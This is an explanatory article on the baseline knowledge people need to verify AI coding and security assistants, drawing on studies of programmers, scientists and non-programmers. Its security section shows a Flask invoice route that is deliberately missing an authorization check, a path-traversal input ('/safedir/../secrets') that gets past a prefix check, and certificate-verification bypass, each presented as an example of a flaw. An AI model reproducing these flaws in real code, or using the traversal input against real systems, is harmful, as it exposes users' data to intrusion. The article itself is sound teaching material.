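# Baseline knowledge and the safe use of AI coding and security assistants

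## What the assistants do and what baseline knowledge means

An AI coding assistant writes, changes or explains computer code on request. A security assistant helps people protect computer systems, for instance by sorting alerts or searching software for weaknesses an attacker could use. Both run on large language models, which learn patterns from large collections of text and code and use them to generate new text. Both can produce work that looks finished but is wrong. Their users include professional programmers and security analysts, as well as students, office staff and people who have never written code. Each time, somebody has to decide whether to rely on the result. Researchers, teachers and employers disagree about how much that person must already know, and about whether heavy use of an assistant keeps people from learning it.

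### Coding assistants

Coding assistants take three forms: completion, chat and agent. Completion came first. When a programmer starts writing a function, for example one that counts the days between two dates, the tool suggests the remaining lines, which the programmer can accept or ignore. GitHub, a platform for storing and sharing code, released a preview of its completion tool, Copilot, in June 2021. *Vibe Coding* (2026), a review of research on AI-assisted programming by Michels, Abu Ghazaleh and colleagues, reports that Codex, the OpenAI model behind Copilot, solved 28.8% of 164 short test problems on the first attempt.

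Users of chat assistants ask questions in ordinary language. For example, a user might paste in a database query that lists the same customer twice, ask why, and get an explanation and a corrected query. Editors such as Cursor build the chat into the programmer's workspace, where the assistant proposes changes and the programmer reviews them before applying them.

An agent takes on a whole task and works through it in many steps with tools. If asked to let customers download their invoices, an agent such as Claude Code reads the project's files, edits several of them, runs the tests, fixes what fails and returns a set of changes. Browser-based builders such as Lovable and Replit go further, letting people who do not program describe an application and receive a working one at a web address. Much of this is vibe coding, a term the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy coined in February 2025 for building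 software by describing it while reading little or none of the code. A month later, the programmer Simon Willison wrote that a person who has reviewed, tested and understood the code is not vibe coding, even if a model wrote every line. Michels and colleagues adopt this distinction.

Each form of assistant gives a person more to check at one time than the one before. Someone who accepts a completion usually has the intended code in mind already and can compare the two in seconds, while an agent may return changes to dozens of files. *When AI builds itself*, published in June 2026 by Anthropic, the maker of the Claude models, illustrates this growth with measurements by the evaluation group METR. In March 2024, Claude Opus 3 could complete software tasks that take a person about four minutes, and two years later Claude Opus 4.6 could complete tasks that take twelve hours. The models succeed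 at tasks of these lengths only half the time, so someone who delegates a twelve-hour task still has to check whether the result is correct.

### Security assistants

The everyday use of security assistants is sorting alerts. A security operations centre (SOC), the team that watches for and responds to attacks on an organisation's systems, receives far more alerts than it can study closely. An assistant might group forty failed logins from one laptop into a single incident, note that the owner changed her password that morning, and rank the incident low. The analyst then has to decide whether the password change really explains the failed logins. Assistants also summarise incidents, so an analyst coming on shift can read a page instead of a thousand log entries.

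Other security assistants look for flaws in software. Anthropic uses an automated reviewer to check every proposed change to its own code for bugs and security defects before it is merged. The company also reports that its restricted model Mythos Preview found more than ten thousand serious vulnerabilities in widely used software in the first weeks of Project Glasswing, a programme for organisations that maintain critical systems.

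### How much code AI writes

The highest figures for AI-written code are self-reported by companies that sell these tools. According to Anthropic, Claude wrote more than 80% of the code that the company merged into its codebase in May 2026, up from the low single digits before February 2025. The company counts lines that reached production and that it can trace to Claude. Its prospectus for a stock-market listing gives a newer figure of over 90% of code contributions in September 2026. Infobae's *Claude escribió más del 90% del código de Anthropic en septiembre* (2026) points out that the prospectus does not define a contribution, and that Anthropic concedes that no third party has verified several of its operating metrics. The two figures may therefore measure different things, so the difference between them can't safely be read as growth.

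Google's chief executive, Sundar Pichai, said in April 2026 that AI generated 75% of the company's new code, up from 50% the previous autumn and 25% in 2024 (Semafor, *Google CEO says 75% of company's new code is AI-generated*, 2026). He added that engineers approve this code, so their work has shifted from writing code toward reviewing it.

No one has measured what share of code AI writes across the whole industry. EconoTimes' *Google Says AI Generated 75% of Its New Code* (2026) cites a survey by Sonar, a company that makes code-checking tools, in which 1,149 technology professionals estimated that AI had generated or significantly assisted 42% of the code they contributed in 2025. Fiona Chen and James Stratton of Harvard analysed work records from more than 700 software companies and found that agents accounted for 10.8% of merge requests (proposed changes to shared code) in March 2026,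 according to UA.News' *AI agents increased code volume, not software releases*. After companies introduced agents, the average wait between proposing a change and merging it grew by 49%, and the share of requests in which reviewers demanded corrections nearly doubled. The 10.8% figure is much lower than the companies' own figures, but it counts whole requests rather than lines and stops in March. Agents have spread fast since then. GitHub reports that they started 17% of such requests on its platform in March and over 40% in September.

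### Four kinds of baseline knowledge

Baseline knowledge means the concepts and skills a person needs to judge an assistant's output in a field without relying on the assistant. To see what this includes, suppose that the agent in the earlier example has finished the invoice page, the tests pass, and the page works when the programmer tries it.

Baseline knowledge begins with programming concepts. Suppose an assistant writes code that loads every invoice in the database and then discards those that belong to other customers. Nobody notices the delay with fifty test records, but with five million the site stalls. To foresee this, the programmer has to know what a query does and how its running time grows with the number of records.

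The page also has a security flaw that only someone who knows security concepts would notice. It checks that the visitor has logged in but not that the invoice belongs to them, so a customer who changes the number at the end of the web address from 1041 to 1042 can download a stranger's invoice.

Baseline knowledge also includes knowledge of the particular system or business. The firm's accountants correct a mistake by issuing a second invoice under the same number, and only the later one counts. The project files don't include this rule, so the agent could not account for it, and the page serves whichever invoice the database returns first.

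The last part of baseline knowledge is a sense of one's own limits. The agent has also added a rule for taxing customers abroad. The programmer has never dealt with foreign tax, knows she cannot judge the rule, and asks a colleague in finance to look at it.

A person can have one of these without the others. Someone can program for twenty years without learning the accountants' custom, and an accountant who spots the duplicate invoice at once may never think of altering a web address. Years of experience are therefore a rough measure of baseline knowledge. A study that groups participants by time in the job may find no difference between the groups because finding the fault required knowledge that the job had never taught them.

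The sense of one's limits is perhaps the least dependable of the four, even among experts. *Educating the Agentic Engineer* (Alenezi, 2026) cites a randomised trial in which experienced open-source developers took 19% longer with the AI tools of early 2025 but believed the tools had made them 20% faster. Current tools may well save such developers time, but those in the trial misjudged their own speed in projects they knew well.

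### Terms for checking and for skill

*Verification* is checking whether an output is correct and fit for its purpose before relying on it. Opening the invoice page and seeing a document appear is weak verification, because the page passes that test even with the security flaw. *Overreliance* is accepting an AI output that is wrong. *Automation bias* is the tendency to favour a machine's suggestion over one's own checking or over contrary evidence. Overreliance can occur without automation bias. A beginner who approves the invoice page because he has never heard of this kind of flaw overrelies on the agent out of ignorance, and teaching him the concept may fix that. An expert who knows the flaw well but approves the page unread because the last thirty changes were fine shows automation bias, and teaching her more about the flaw will probably help little.

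*Calibration* is how closely a person's confidence matches how often that person is right. A reviewer who feels 90% sure of each approval and is right about nine in ten of them is well calibrated. Poor calibration leads overconfident reviewers to skip checks that would have found problems and underconfident reviewers to throw away good work.

The remaining terms concern how people's skills change over time. *Skill formation* is gaining a new skill, and *deskilling* is losing a skill through lack of practice. A student who never learns to trace a program's steps because an assistant always does it has not been deskilled, because they never had the skill. To observe either process, a researcher has to remove the assistant and measure *unassisted performance*, or how well the person does the task alone, because people can do good work with an assistant whether or not they have the skill themselves.

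### Bainbridge's argument

The worry that automation takes away the practice people need in order to check its work long predates language models. Lisanne Bainbridge, a psychologist at University College London, described it in *Ironies of Automation* (1983), a paper about computer-controlled industrial plants, with some examples from aircraft cockpits.

Her reasoning starts with the tasks left to the human operator. A designer who considers the operator unreliable automates as much as possible and leaves the operator the tasks the designer could not work out how to automate, mainly watching the machine and taking over when it fails.

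Taking over requires manual skill and an understanding of how the plant behaves, and both fade without use. An operator who once ran the process manually but has since spent years monitoring it may handle it like a novice. People recall knowledge quickly only if they use it often, and they develop it only by using it and getting feedback on what worked. Bainbridge expected little from classroom theory without exercises. Operators have to take over when something has already gone wrong, so they need more skill than on an ordinary day, even though their skill has faded from lack of practice.

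Watching is no easier, because experiments on vigilance had shown that even a highly motivated person cannot keep effective visual attention for more than about half an hour on a display where almost nothing happens. The operator is also supposed to confirm that the computer's decisions are right, even though the plant uses the computer because it makes certain decisions better or faster than he can. He cannot redo them in time, so he can only judge whether the results look acceptable.

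Bainbridge also saw that the problem could stay hidden for a generation, because the first people to supervise automated plants had learned the work by hand. The new systems were "riding on their skills", which their successors could not be expected to have. She proposed that operators take manual control for part of every shift or, if that was impossible, practise on a simulator. The most reliable systems might need the greatest investment in training, because their operators so rarely have anything to do. Researchers have since tested whether airline pilots' skills fade in this way.

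Alenezi applies Bainbridge's argument directly to engineers who supervise agents, and Anthropic's own staff have described similar experiences. One employee had not written any code for about five months. Another described days when everything breaks and "I have no idea what I've been up to anymore". These anecdotes show only that the situation Bainbridge described can arise in software.

A plant keeps running while its operator thinks, but a proposed change to a program can wait while the reviewer runs it, thinks it over or asks a colleague. Bainbridge concluded that people can be impressive problem solvers when they are not under time pressure, and that the difficulty lies in acting fast. Her points about attention and speed therefore fit an SOC analyst in the middle of an attack better than a programmer who can take their time. Her point about lost practice applies to both, and it may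 matter more as assistants improve. She noted that operators who deal with alarms all day get plenty of experience. Someone who has to correct an assistant every day likewise stays in practice, though the mistakes cause problems of their own, while someone who has to correct it twice a year does not.

### The strong and the weak claim

Some people conclude from such reasoning that nobody should use these tools without the baseline knowledge to judge their output. Others draw the weaker conclusion that risk rises as knowledge falls.

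Alenezi comes close to the strong version when he writes that "supervision without comprehension is vacuous", but he offers this as a reason to keep teaching foundations and does not propose a ban. To justify a ban, one would have to show that users below some level of knowledge miss the faults that matter, that no test, scanner or colleague would catch those faults instead, and that the harm outweighs what the users gain. The last condition fails in some cases. A retired teacher who vibe-codes a catalogue of her record collection, on her own computer and with nobody else's data in it, risks only an inaccurate catalogue. A clinic that puts patient files behind a vibe-coded login page risks far more. Bainbridge's argument is not enough to justify a rule that treats the two alike.

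The weak version is a factual claim that researchers can test by giving the same faulty output to people who know more and people who know less, and counting who notices the faults. It could be false, because experts might trust the machine as readily as beginners do, or might cancel their advantage by giving it larger and more dangerous tasks. The experience of Daniel Stenberg, who created the data-transfer tool curl, is weaker evidence for the claim than it first seems. Michels and colleagues report that he ended curl's programme of rewards for reported flaws after six years because worthless AI-written bug reports took up so much of the maintainers' time, yet he credits AI, when skilled people use it, with finding deep vulnerabilities that no earlier tool had found. But because the programme paid money, some people may have sent in junk knowing that they had not checked it.

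Good evidence for the weak version would not establish the strong version. A hospital could accept that a ward clerk runs a higher risk with a coding agent than a programmer does, and still let the clerk use it if someone who can read the code reviews the program before it accesses a patient's record.

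## How people detect wrong output, and what missing knowledge changes

A hospital that lets a ward clerk use a coding agent, provided that a programmer reviews the result, relies on the programmer to notice faults. In *Programmers Are Poor and Overconfident Judges of LLM-Generated Assertions*, Kaufman, Murali and colleagues (2026) gave programmers a small version of that job, and the programmers accepted about half of the faulty code. One short program from the experiment shows how much a person has to do to catch a single fault.

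### The steps of checking

The program, `common`, takes two lists and returns the items that occur in both, sorted and without repeats. A language model wrote an assertion for it, a line of code that raises an error if a condition is false when the line runs. The assertion contains a mistake. It goes through the first list and keeps each item that also occurs in the second list and occurs exactly once in the returned list. Then it sorts the kept items and checks that they match the returned list.

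To find the mistake, a programmer needs to know what a right answer looks like. If the first list is 1, 1, 2 and the second is 1, 4, `common` should return a single 1. Working that out requires understanding the task and, in a firm's own software, the firm's rules. People who can't work it out may instead judge the code by whether it looks familiar. In *How Beginning Programmers and Code LLMs (Mis)read Each Other* (2024), 20 of 33 students at Wellesley College said that code with a compact way of building lists resembled what they would write themselves, compared with 9 of 24 at Oberlin College. Familiarity probably reflects what a course has covered, and is a poor guide to correctness. *I Would Have Written My Code Differently* (2025) reports that students in a first programming course misread model-written code partly because its style was new to them, and also overestimated how often it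 was correct.

A programmer who knows what to expect can check the output against each requirement in turn. In the assertion for `common`, the test for "exactly once" counts occurrences in the returned list, where each item occurs once anyway, but the repeats are in the first list. Only someone who works out what the code does will notice this. A reader with a weaker grasp of the language matches the wording of the assertion to the wording of the requirements, and the assertion then looks correct because it seems to have a part for each requirement, including the one that forbids repeats. Comparison also works badly when the output leaves something out, because the reader has nothing to compare with the requirement.

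A programmer in doubt can look for a counterexample, meaning an input on which the output fails. Given the lists [1, 1, 2] and [1, 4], the assertion keeps both 1s from the first list, compares [1, 1] with the correct answer from `common`, [1], and wrongly raises an error. To choose that input, the programmer has to know where programs tend to break, for instance on repeated values and empty lists. People who don't know this usually run the code and see whether it works. The description of `common` includes two worked examples, and the faulty assertion passes both because neither has a repeated item in its first list.

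Running the code is the most common check even among people who program regularly. *How Researchers Use and Verify AI Coding Assistants* (O'Brien, Milewicz and Eisty, 2026) analysed 506 accounts in which scientists, most of them at American universities, described using an AI tool for one programming task in 2025. The scientists reported running the code in 52.8% of the accounts, reading it in 19.4%, using automated tests in 2.8% and having another person review it in 2.0%. The true rates may be higher, because the scientists chose which checks to mention. Running code can be a serious test. One scientist ran the program on two small data files, made so that the answers were easy to work out by hand. Others reported only that no error had appeared, which is the check that the faulty assertion passes.

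Once something looks wrong, the programmer has to find the cause and judge whether a repair removes it. This diagnosis takes a working model of how the parts of the program produce the result. Without one, people can paste the error message back into the assistant and accept the next version if the message goes away. In O'Brien and colleagues' accounts of debugging, 31 of 88 scientists reported running the code as their only check on the fix. Learning with an assistant may also harm diagnosis more than any other step, since *How AI Impacts Skill Formation* (Shen and Tamkin, 2026) found the largest gap between learners with and without AI on debugging questions.

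The last step is deciding whether to accept the output, reject it, check further or ask someone. This draws on knowledge of what depends on the result and a sense of one's own limits. *The Metacognitive Demands and Opportunities of Generative AI* (2023) treats such judgements as metacognition, the monitoring and steering of one's own thinking. People may instead decide based on a fluent explanation or a deadline. One scientist in O'Brien and colleagues' survey admitted that the longer and more complicated a piece of work became, the less they read the code and the more they just ran it to see what happened.

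### What 86 programmers caught

Kaufman and colleagues took 26 short Python functions from HumanEval, the problem set OpenAI had used to test Codex. Each function had one correct and one incorrect assertion, all written by OpenAI's GPT-3.5 or GPT-4. An assertion counted as correct if it never raised an error on a right result, even if it missed some wrong ones. For example, the correct assertion for `common` checks that every returned item is in both input lists and that the returned list is sorted without repeats, so it would accept an empty list even when the two lists share items.

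The 86 participants could all read Python, and two-thirds were professional developers. For each of ten functions, they read a description and an assertion, judged whether the assertion was correct and how complete it was, and rated their confidence. They accepted 73.9% of the correct assertions but rejected only 49.0% of the incorrect ones. For the function `common`, 92% recognised the correct assertion, but only 10% caught the incorrect one.

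Participants who rejected an incorrect assertion spent an average of 123 seconds on it, compared with 97 seconds for those who accepted it. With correct assertions, participants took about the same time whether they judged rightly or wrongly. These times fit the idea that finding a fault takes extra steps, but they don't prove that slowing down would help, because participants may have spent the extra seconds confirming a fault they already suspected.

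Some of the assertions came with a comment in plain English. Kaufman and colleagues had predicted that comments would help, but even those that described the assertion exactly did not. Readers were less accurate with comments that left out part of what the assertion does than with exact ones. The incomplete comments also raised their confidence to 4.25 out of 5, from 3.99 with no comment. One such comment for `common` mentions that the returned items occur in both lists and are sorted, but omits that they must be unique. A reader who checks only what the comment mentions will think they are done too early. The loss of accuracy is a modest result (p = 0.037, uncorrected for multiple comparisons) and needs to be replicated. For anyone who hopes that an assistant can make up for missing knowledge by explaining its own code, it matters more that exact comments did not help.

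To learn how people reach these judgements, Kaufman and colleagues asked ten more programmers to think aloud while working through five of the functions. The programmers compared clauses, traced the logic, tried inputs that should pass, tried inputs that should fail, or relied on intuition. They used a failing example in 18 of the 29 cases where they judged an assertion to be wrong, and in 14 of those 18 the example confirmed a suspicion they already had. So they seldom looked for a counterexample to an assertion that seemed fine, which makes them least likely to catch a plausible mistake like the one in `common`. Intuition played a part in 12 of the 50 judgements, and 7 of those 12 were wrong.

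The ten programmers got 39 of their 50 judgements right, a better rate than the survey participants on the same five functions. Having to explain each step aloud may have led them to take steps they would otherwise have skipped. They were also fairly experienced, and ten people are too few to tell which of the two factors mattered.

Kaufman and colleagues suggest that people may lean towards accepting AI suggestions, or that it is harder to refute a logical statement than to confirm one. The experiment cannot separate these explanations because a model wrote every assertion. If programmers miss just as many faults in assertions their colleagues wrote, the problem lies in reading code and has little to do with automation bias. Kaufman and colleagues designed the study to test comments and noticed the gap between correct and incorrect assertions only after they had begun their analysis, though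 the gap is large enough that chance is an unlikely explanation.

### The numbers as signal detection

Signal detection theory, a method from psychology, measures separately how well people can distinguish two things and how readily they report one of them. Here the signal is a wrong assertion. The hit rate, the share of wrong assertions that people reject, is 0.49. The false-alarm rate, the share of correct assertions that they reject, is 1 − 0.739 = 0.261.

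In the theory's simplest model, every assertion arouses some degree of suspicion in the reviewer, and wrong ones arouse more on average. Suspicion varies along a bell curve for each group, the two curves have the same width, and the reviewer rejects anything above a certain threshold. The distance between the centres of the curves, in standard deviations, is called d′ and measures the ability to tell wrong from right:

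d′ = z(hit rate) − z(false-alarm rate) = −0.025 − (−0.640) ≈ 0.62

The function z converts a proportion into a position on the standard bell curve. A d′ of zero would mean that reviewers reject wrong and correct assertions equally often, as they would by chance. With a d′ of 0.62, an unbiased reviewer would judge about 62% of assertions correctly, so the programmers did only a little better than chance. The criterion, which measures their bias, is minus the average of the two z values, or about 0.33. A positive value means that they set a high threshold for rejecting assertions and tended to accept them.

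Suppose an assistant produces 100 outputs and 10 are wrong. At these rates, the reviewer rejects about 5 of the wrong outputs and about 23 of the 90 correct ones. Review lowers the error rate from 10% to about 7% among the roughly 72 outputs that are accepted, but the reviewer also rejects nearly five correct outputs for every wrong one caught.

The same arithmetic shows why telling reviewers to be stricter isn't enough. With d′ fixed at 0.62, a reviewer who caught nine in ten wrong outputs would also reject about three-quarters of the sound ones. Being stricter only moves the threshold for rejection. To catch more faults without rejecting more good work, reviewers have to get better at telling the two apart. Baseline knowledge, a good test or a better method of checking would have to produce that improvement.

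All this is an illustration, because it pools the answers of 86 people about 52 different assertions. The five functions in the think-aloud study show how much the pooling hides. The percentages come from the main experiment:

| Function | What it should do | Rejected the wrong assertion | Accepted the correct assertion |
|---|---|---|---|
| `common` | return the items that two lists share | 10% | 92% |
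| `has_close_elements` | report whether any two numbers are closer than a threshold | 18% | 77% |
| `choose_num` | find the largest even number in a range | 60% | 61% |
| `any_int` | check that three whole numbers include one that is the sum of the others | 75% | 82% |
| `match_parens` | report whether two strings of brackets can join into a balanced one | 82% | 18% |

On `common`, people accepted almost everything, and on `match_parens` they rejected almost everything. They could not tell the right assertion from the wrong one in either case. They did well on `any_int`, because they could easily see whether each requirement appeared in the assertion. Only about fourteen people on average judged each assertion, so the individual percentages are rough, but they suggest that how well a programmer checks depends heavily on the kind of fault. Half of the assertions in the experiment were wrong,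 and people might well check less carefully at work, where most outputs may be sound.

### Why experience made no difference

Kaufman and colleagues found no evidence that years of experience, skill in Python, practice in writing assertions or use of language models predicted how accurately people judged model output. Among the studies of checking by people who can read the code, this is the strongest evidence against the claim that knowing more makes using an assistant safer. The participants judged real model output with a known right answer, whereas much of the evidence for the claim comes from what people say about themselves.

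The analysis was exploratory, though, the study was designed for another purpose, and a sample of this size can miss a useful advantage. If the 86 participants were split into a more and a less experienced half, each half would have judged about 180 wrong assertions. Chance alone could then separate their catch rates by some ten percentage points, or more after allowing for differences between individuals. The study could easily have missed a true ten-point advantage for the experienced half, but would probably have detected a thirty-point one. The result is therefore good evidence that experience, within this group, doesn't turn a poor judge of assertions into a reliable one.

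The finding has less bearing on people outside the group. Everyone in the experiment could read Python, and most had programmed for between one and ten years, so it does not show that someone who has never programmed would do as well. The task also gave experienced programmers no particular advantage, because the functions involved no business rules, security or large systems, which are the areas where long service in a job teaches something. Only one of the ten think-aloud participants reported substantial experience of writing assertions, so even the most experienced programmers may have had little practice at the skill being tested.

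Experience may matter more when programmers have to find and repair a fault. *Do AI models help produce verified bug fixes?* (2025) describes an experiment in which programmers debugged with or without GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model, and a mathematical proof tool checked whether each fix met the specification. Programmers without the model did as well or better on most measures. Experts often sensed that the model's answer was false and ignored it, but novices were at serious risk of accepting it and failing. Complete novices did benefit from the model on simple bugs. The paper acknowledges that the sample was small, and GPT-4o mini was far weaker than current models. This result and that of Kaufman and colleagues can both be true, because an expert may recognise a bad repair from the understanding of the program she gained while debugging it, but may have no such understanding of an unfamiliar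 assertion she sees for two minutes.

Among the scientists O'Brien and colleagues studied, years of programming had no relation to the number of checks a scientist reported (r = −0.03) or to which of the common checks they used. But a count of checks doesn't measure their quality. An experienced programmer who looks at a graph may notice an impossible trend that a student would miss, and both would appear in the data as having inspected a graph.

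### People without the baseline

Virk and Liu (2025), in *Non-programmers Assessing AI-Generated Code*, studied people who knew far less about programming than the participants in Kaufman and colleagues' experiment. They recruited ten marketing and sales professionals with no professional programming or data science experience, and showed them a model's answers to eight questions about 27 weeks of sales data from a fictional television company. The participants never saw the code, only a plain-language account of the method and results, which Virk and Liu had corrected by hand to match the code.

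Virk and Liu tried to make participants suspicious of the AI's answers. Each task carried a highlighted warning that the AI often makes mistakes and that some might be hard to notice, so they had good reason to expect errors. Participants had to restate the method in their own words and then list its shortcomings, and the three best performers received a $6 bonus on top of their $8.

The ten participants still missed serious flaws that can be seen without knowing statistics. In one task, the model had to find the best price between $800 and $1,200 but tried only $1,000, and half of the participants noticed. In another, it looked for the cause of sudden peaks in sales without considering holidays. Most participants missed this, although a marketer knows that holidays drive sales. All ten missed the flaw in a third task, where the model had to adjust advertising and other factors to maximise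 sales. It kept every factor within its historical range, which rules out the obvious option of spending more on advertising than ever before.

Knowing statistics would have helped participants catch another flaw, but it wasn't necessary. The model chose between two ways of predicting sales by their mean squared error, the average of the squared differences between predicted and actual values, and reported an error of about 133,936,095 for the better one. Someone who knows the measure takes the square root, gets a typical miss of about 11,600, and compares that with an ordinary week's sales to judge whether the forecast is useful, since the better method could still be a bad one. Someone who doesn't know the measure can still object that the answer never explains whether such a number is good or bad, and Virk and Liu consider general critical thinking enough to spot the problem. A marketing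 associate who read this answer saw no obvious deficiency and called the comparison of two models a productive idea. One manager objected to a sound step, wanting more data for testing the model than for building it, a misunderstanding that would lead a reviewer to reject good work.

Participants who missed the holiday flaw almost certainly knew the relevant fact but failed to apply it, because a description of methods they did not understand obscured its relevance. They also flagged wrong statements more often than omissions, as one would expect if they were checking the text only against itself and had no answer of their own to compare it with. A reviewer who knows the business may therefore also need to understand enough of the technical side to see where that knowledge applies.

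To help people find flaws, Virk and Liu then gave 18 new participants answers laid out in separate steps, and nine of them also saw two alternative methods beside each step. Eight of the nine who saw only the steps noticed that the model had tried only one price, compared with five of ten earlier participants. Only four of the nine who also saw alternatives noticed, perhaps because the extra technical text made a simple mistake harder to notice. On four other tasks, the people who saw alternatives found the most flaws. The groups were too small to say which layout is better. Neither professional experience nor time spent explained why only some people made good use of the alternatives.

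Virk and Liu tested no data analysts for comparison, so their results show that these professionals could not check the work reliably, but not how much better a trained person would have done. Kaufman and colleagues' figures are a reason not to assume that the difference would be large. The people in both experiments were also judging unfamiliar material with nothing of their own at stake, and might notice more in data from their own company.

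#### Vibe coders with and without experience

*From Prompting to Verification* (Fawzy, Tahir and Blincoe, 2026) surveyed 162 people who practise vibe coding and compared them by level of experience. A third had no programming background, a third were novices with some coursework or small projects, and a third were professional developers. All three groups tended to agree that the generated code is useful for prototypes, often flawed, and sometimes wrong while looking right.

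When an error appeared, people without a background were more likely than professionals to ask the AI again instead of debugging by hand. They were also more likely to give up because they could not understand the code. About 45% of professionals said they always check AI code before using it, and the only people who said they never check it had no background. Fawzy and colleagues call this a gap between perception and action. In terms of the checking steps, users without a background know that faults exist but get stuck at diagnosis.

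The groups differed little, and on several measures not at all. All three agreed about equally that they usually run the code once to see if it works, and they reported similar trust in code they did not fully understand. When Fawzy and colleagues added hours of vibe coding, length of use and hours of coding without AI to their analysis, the group labels no longer predicted anything. People who did more coding without AI asked the AI again less often and checked its code more often. No single factor stood out as a predictor of giving up on code they could not understand. This suggests that current practice in writing code matters more than whether someone counts as a professional, although people who like to check code may also be the ones who like to write it.

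The survey relied on self-reported habits, and professionals may feel more pressure to claim that they always check. Agreeing that AI code is "often flawed" also shows only limited awareness, because a person can agree without knowing what a missing access check is or where to look for one.

#### Beginners

The earlier 2024 study of students at Wellesley, Oberlin and elsewhere suggested the same thing. Beginners judged model-written code 960 times and called it correct 61.8% of the time. In 91% of the cases they called correct, the code had passed every test. The students may have read the code well or just followed the test results, and the figures fit either explanation. Following the tests is sensible when someone competent wrote them, but a vibe coder with no background usually has no such tests, or only ones the assistant wrote.

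*The Widening Gap* (Prather and colleagues, 2024) used observation and eye tracking to study novice programmers as they worked with AI tools. Students who already knew what they wanted to write used the tools to finish sooner and ignored bad suggestions. Struggling students accepted code without validating it and finished believing they understood more than they did. Today's tools make fewer mistakes in beginners' exercises than those of 2024, so a struggling student now sees fewer bad suggestions but may still not recognise them.

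### Confidence and being right

A reviewer who misses faults could still be safe if she knew when she was unsure, because she could then ask for help. In Kaufman and colleagues' study, programmers' average confidence was between 3.98 and 4.14 out of 5, whether or not the assertion was correct and whether or not they had judged it correctly. A participant therefore could not have used her own certainty to pick out the judgements that needed a second look. The paper's title calls the programmers overconfident, which goes slightly beyond the data, since a rating of 4 out of 5 is not a claim to be right 80% of the time.

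Other experiments measure how well people judge their own performance after working with an assistant. Fernandes, Welsch and colleagues at Aalto University in Finland had people solve logical reasoning problems with ChatGPT. Dolan (2025) reports in *Users of generative AI struggle to accurately assess their own competence* that the participants scored higher than people working alone but consistently overestimated their results. *Beyond the Steeper Curve* (2026) puts the gain at about three points and the overestimate at about four. In tests without AI, the weakest performers usually overestimate themselves the most. HIIT, a Finnish research institute, reports in *AI use makes us overestimate our cognitive performance* that this pattern disappeared with ChatGPT and people at all skill levels overestimated themselves. In *Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?* (2023), Perry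 and colleagues also found that people with an assistant wrote less secure code but were more likely to believe it was secure.

*Designing Against Deskilling* (2026) reports a larger and more recent experiment that did not find this effect. Its 704 participants worked without AI, with an AI assistant alone, or with an assistant plus feedback or rewards meant to keep them thinking for themselves. All of them predicted their scores on a final test, and the researchers subtracted each prediction from the actual score, giving a result between −6 and 6. People underestimated themselves in every condition, by an average of 0.93 points without AI and 0.53 points with AI alone. The differences between conditions were small enough to be due to chance.

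The same experiment measured the probability that a person was more confident in a right answer than in a wrong one, where 0.5 is chance. This probability was 0.75 without AI and 0.70 with AI alone, again with no significant difference between the conditions. The researchers had to leave out many participants whose answers were all right or all wrong, so this result is based on fewer people.

The two sets of results may differ because people judged different things. In the Aalto study, they estimated how well they had done with ChatGPT's help, and someone who reads a fluent answer and agrees with it can easily feel they have checked it. In the newer experiment, they predicted their score on a later test. It is too early to conclude that AI makes people overconfident in general. The evidence is stronger for overconfidence about work done with an assistant, which is also the more relevant danger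 for verification.

Claims that people are well calibrated also depend on what the researchers measured. *Metacognition and Confidence Dynamics in Advice Taking from Generative AI* (2025) concludes that its participants were calibrated and that AI advice did not change this. Its evidence is that participants with more confidence in themselves gave more accurate answers. This is a weaker property than calibration in the usual sense, because it would also appear if everyone overrated themselves by the same amount. Participants' confidence in the AI had no relation to accuracy.

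In O'Brien and colleagues' study, scientists' confidence varied with their programming experience, but the checks they made did not. Those with less than about four years of experience tended to trust the AI with the task more than themselves, while those with more tended to trust themselves more. Experienced scientists also felt somewhat more confident that they could evaluate the output. But this confidence was not reliably related to which checks people reported or how many. It correlated with their confidence in doing the task alone (r = 0.30) and in the AI (r = 0.33). A scientist who trusted the AI and felt able to judge its output might have done no more than run the code once.

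## Security flaws in AI-generated code

A scientist who runs an assistant's code once and trusts the result will at least notice a crash, but security flaws are rarely so visible. The code works for honest users, and the flaw appears only when someone uses the program in a way its builder never intended. Often every line is correct but a necessary one is missing, which is the kind of omission that the marketing professionals in Virk and Liu's study tended to overlook.

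### A missing authorization check

The invoice page described earlier has a flaw of this kind. In Python, with the web framework Flask, the code might look like this:

```python
@app.get("/invoices/<int:number>")
@login_required
def show_invoice(number):
    invoice = db.get_or_404(Invoice, number)
    return render_template("invoice.html", invoice=invoice)
```

The first line takes the invoice number from the web address. The second turns away visitors who have not logged in, which is authentication, or establishing who somebody is. The last two lines fetch the invoice and display it. The code never decides whether this customer may see this invoice, which is authorization. That is why changing the number in the address opens a stranger's invoice. The missing line belongs between fetching and displaying:

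```python
    if invoice.customer_id != current_user.id: abort(404)
```

It compares the invoice's owner with the person who has logged in and, if they differ, responds as if the invoice did not exist.

Automated tests can miss this flaw as easily as a programmer glancing at the page. A test that logs in as a customer and opens that customer's invoice passes with or without the extra line. Customers don't complain, because they follow links to their own invoices. A test that logs in as one customer and requests another's invoice would expose the flaw, but people write that test only if they have already thought of the danger.

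A knowledgeable reviewer would ask, "Who may see this invoice, and which line enforces that?" Because she starts from the rule and looks for the code that enforces it, she can notice when that code is missing. She would also ask how the program knows who is making the request. Suppose the assistant had added a check that compares the invoice's owner with a customer number sent by the browser. An attacker could pass this check by sending the owner's number, even though the code looks like authorization. To catch the flaw, the reviewer has to know which values a visitor controls and which the server stored at login.

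Some insecure code seems to work better than the secure version. Mousavi, Islam and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding the Impact of AI Code Assistants on Security API Usage*, describe a common mistake in programs that open an encrypted connection. The program should check the server's certificate, which proves the server's identity. If the programmer sets it to accept every certificate, the connection succeeds without certificate errors, but an attacker between the two machines can pose as the server and read all the traffic.

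### Asking beforehand and spotting afterwards

Someone who understands authorization can tell the assistant, before it writes the code, that customers may open only their own invoices, but she has to remember the danger when nothing on the screen suggests it. She can also notice afterwards that the code lacks this check, if she reads it closely enough to see what it would allow.

A person can tell an assistant about a security requirement and still not notice that the code it returns fails to meet it. In *Do Users Write More Insecure Code with AI Assistants?*, Perry, Srivastava and colleagues (2022) asked people to write a function that opens files only if they are inside a folder called `/safedir`. One participant gave the assistant that requirement and accepted the function it returned, which checked whether the file's path began with `/safedir`. The path `/safedir/../secrets` passes that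 check, but `..` means "go up one folder", so the path leads to `/secrets`, outside the permitted folder. The program has to work out where a path leads before comparing it with the permitted folder.

Few people ask for secure code. Only 1% of the prompts in that experiment mentioned security. Mousavi and colleagues told the 44 professional developers they studied that security would be evaluated, but only two considered it in their prompts. Asking for specific protections can remove some flaws, but not reliably.

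### Two early experiments

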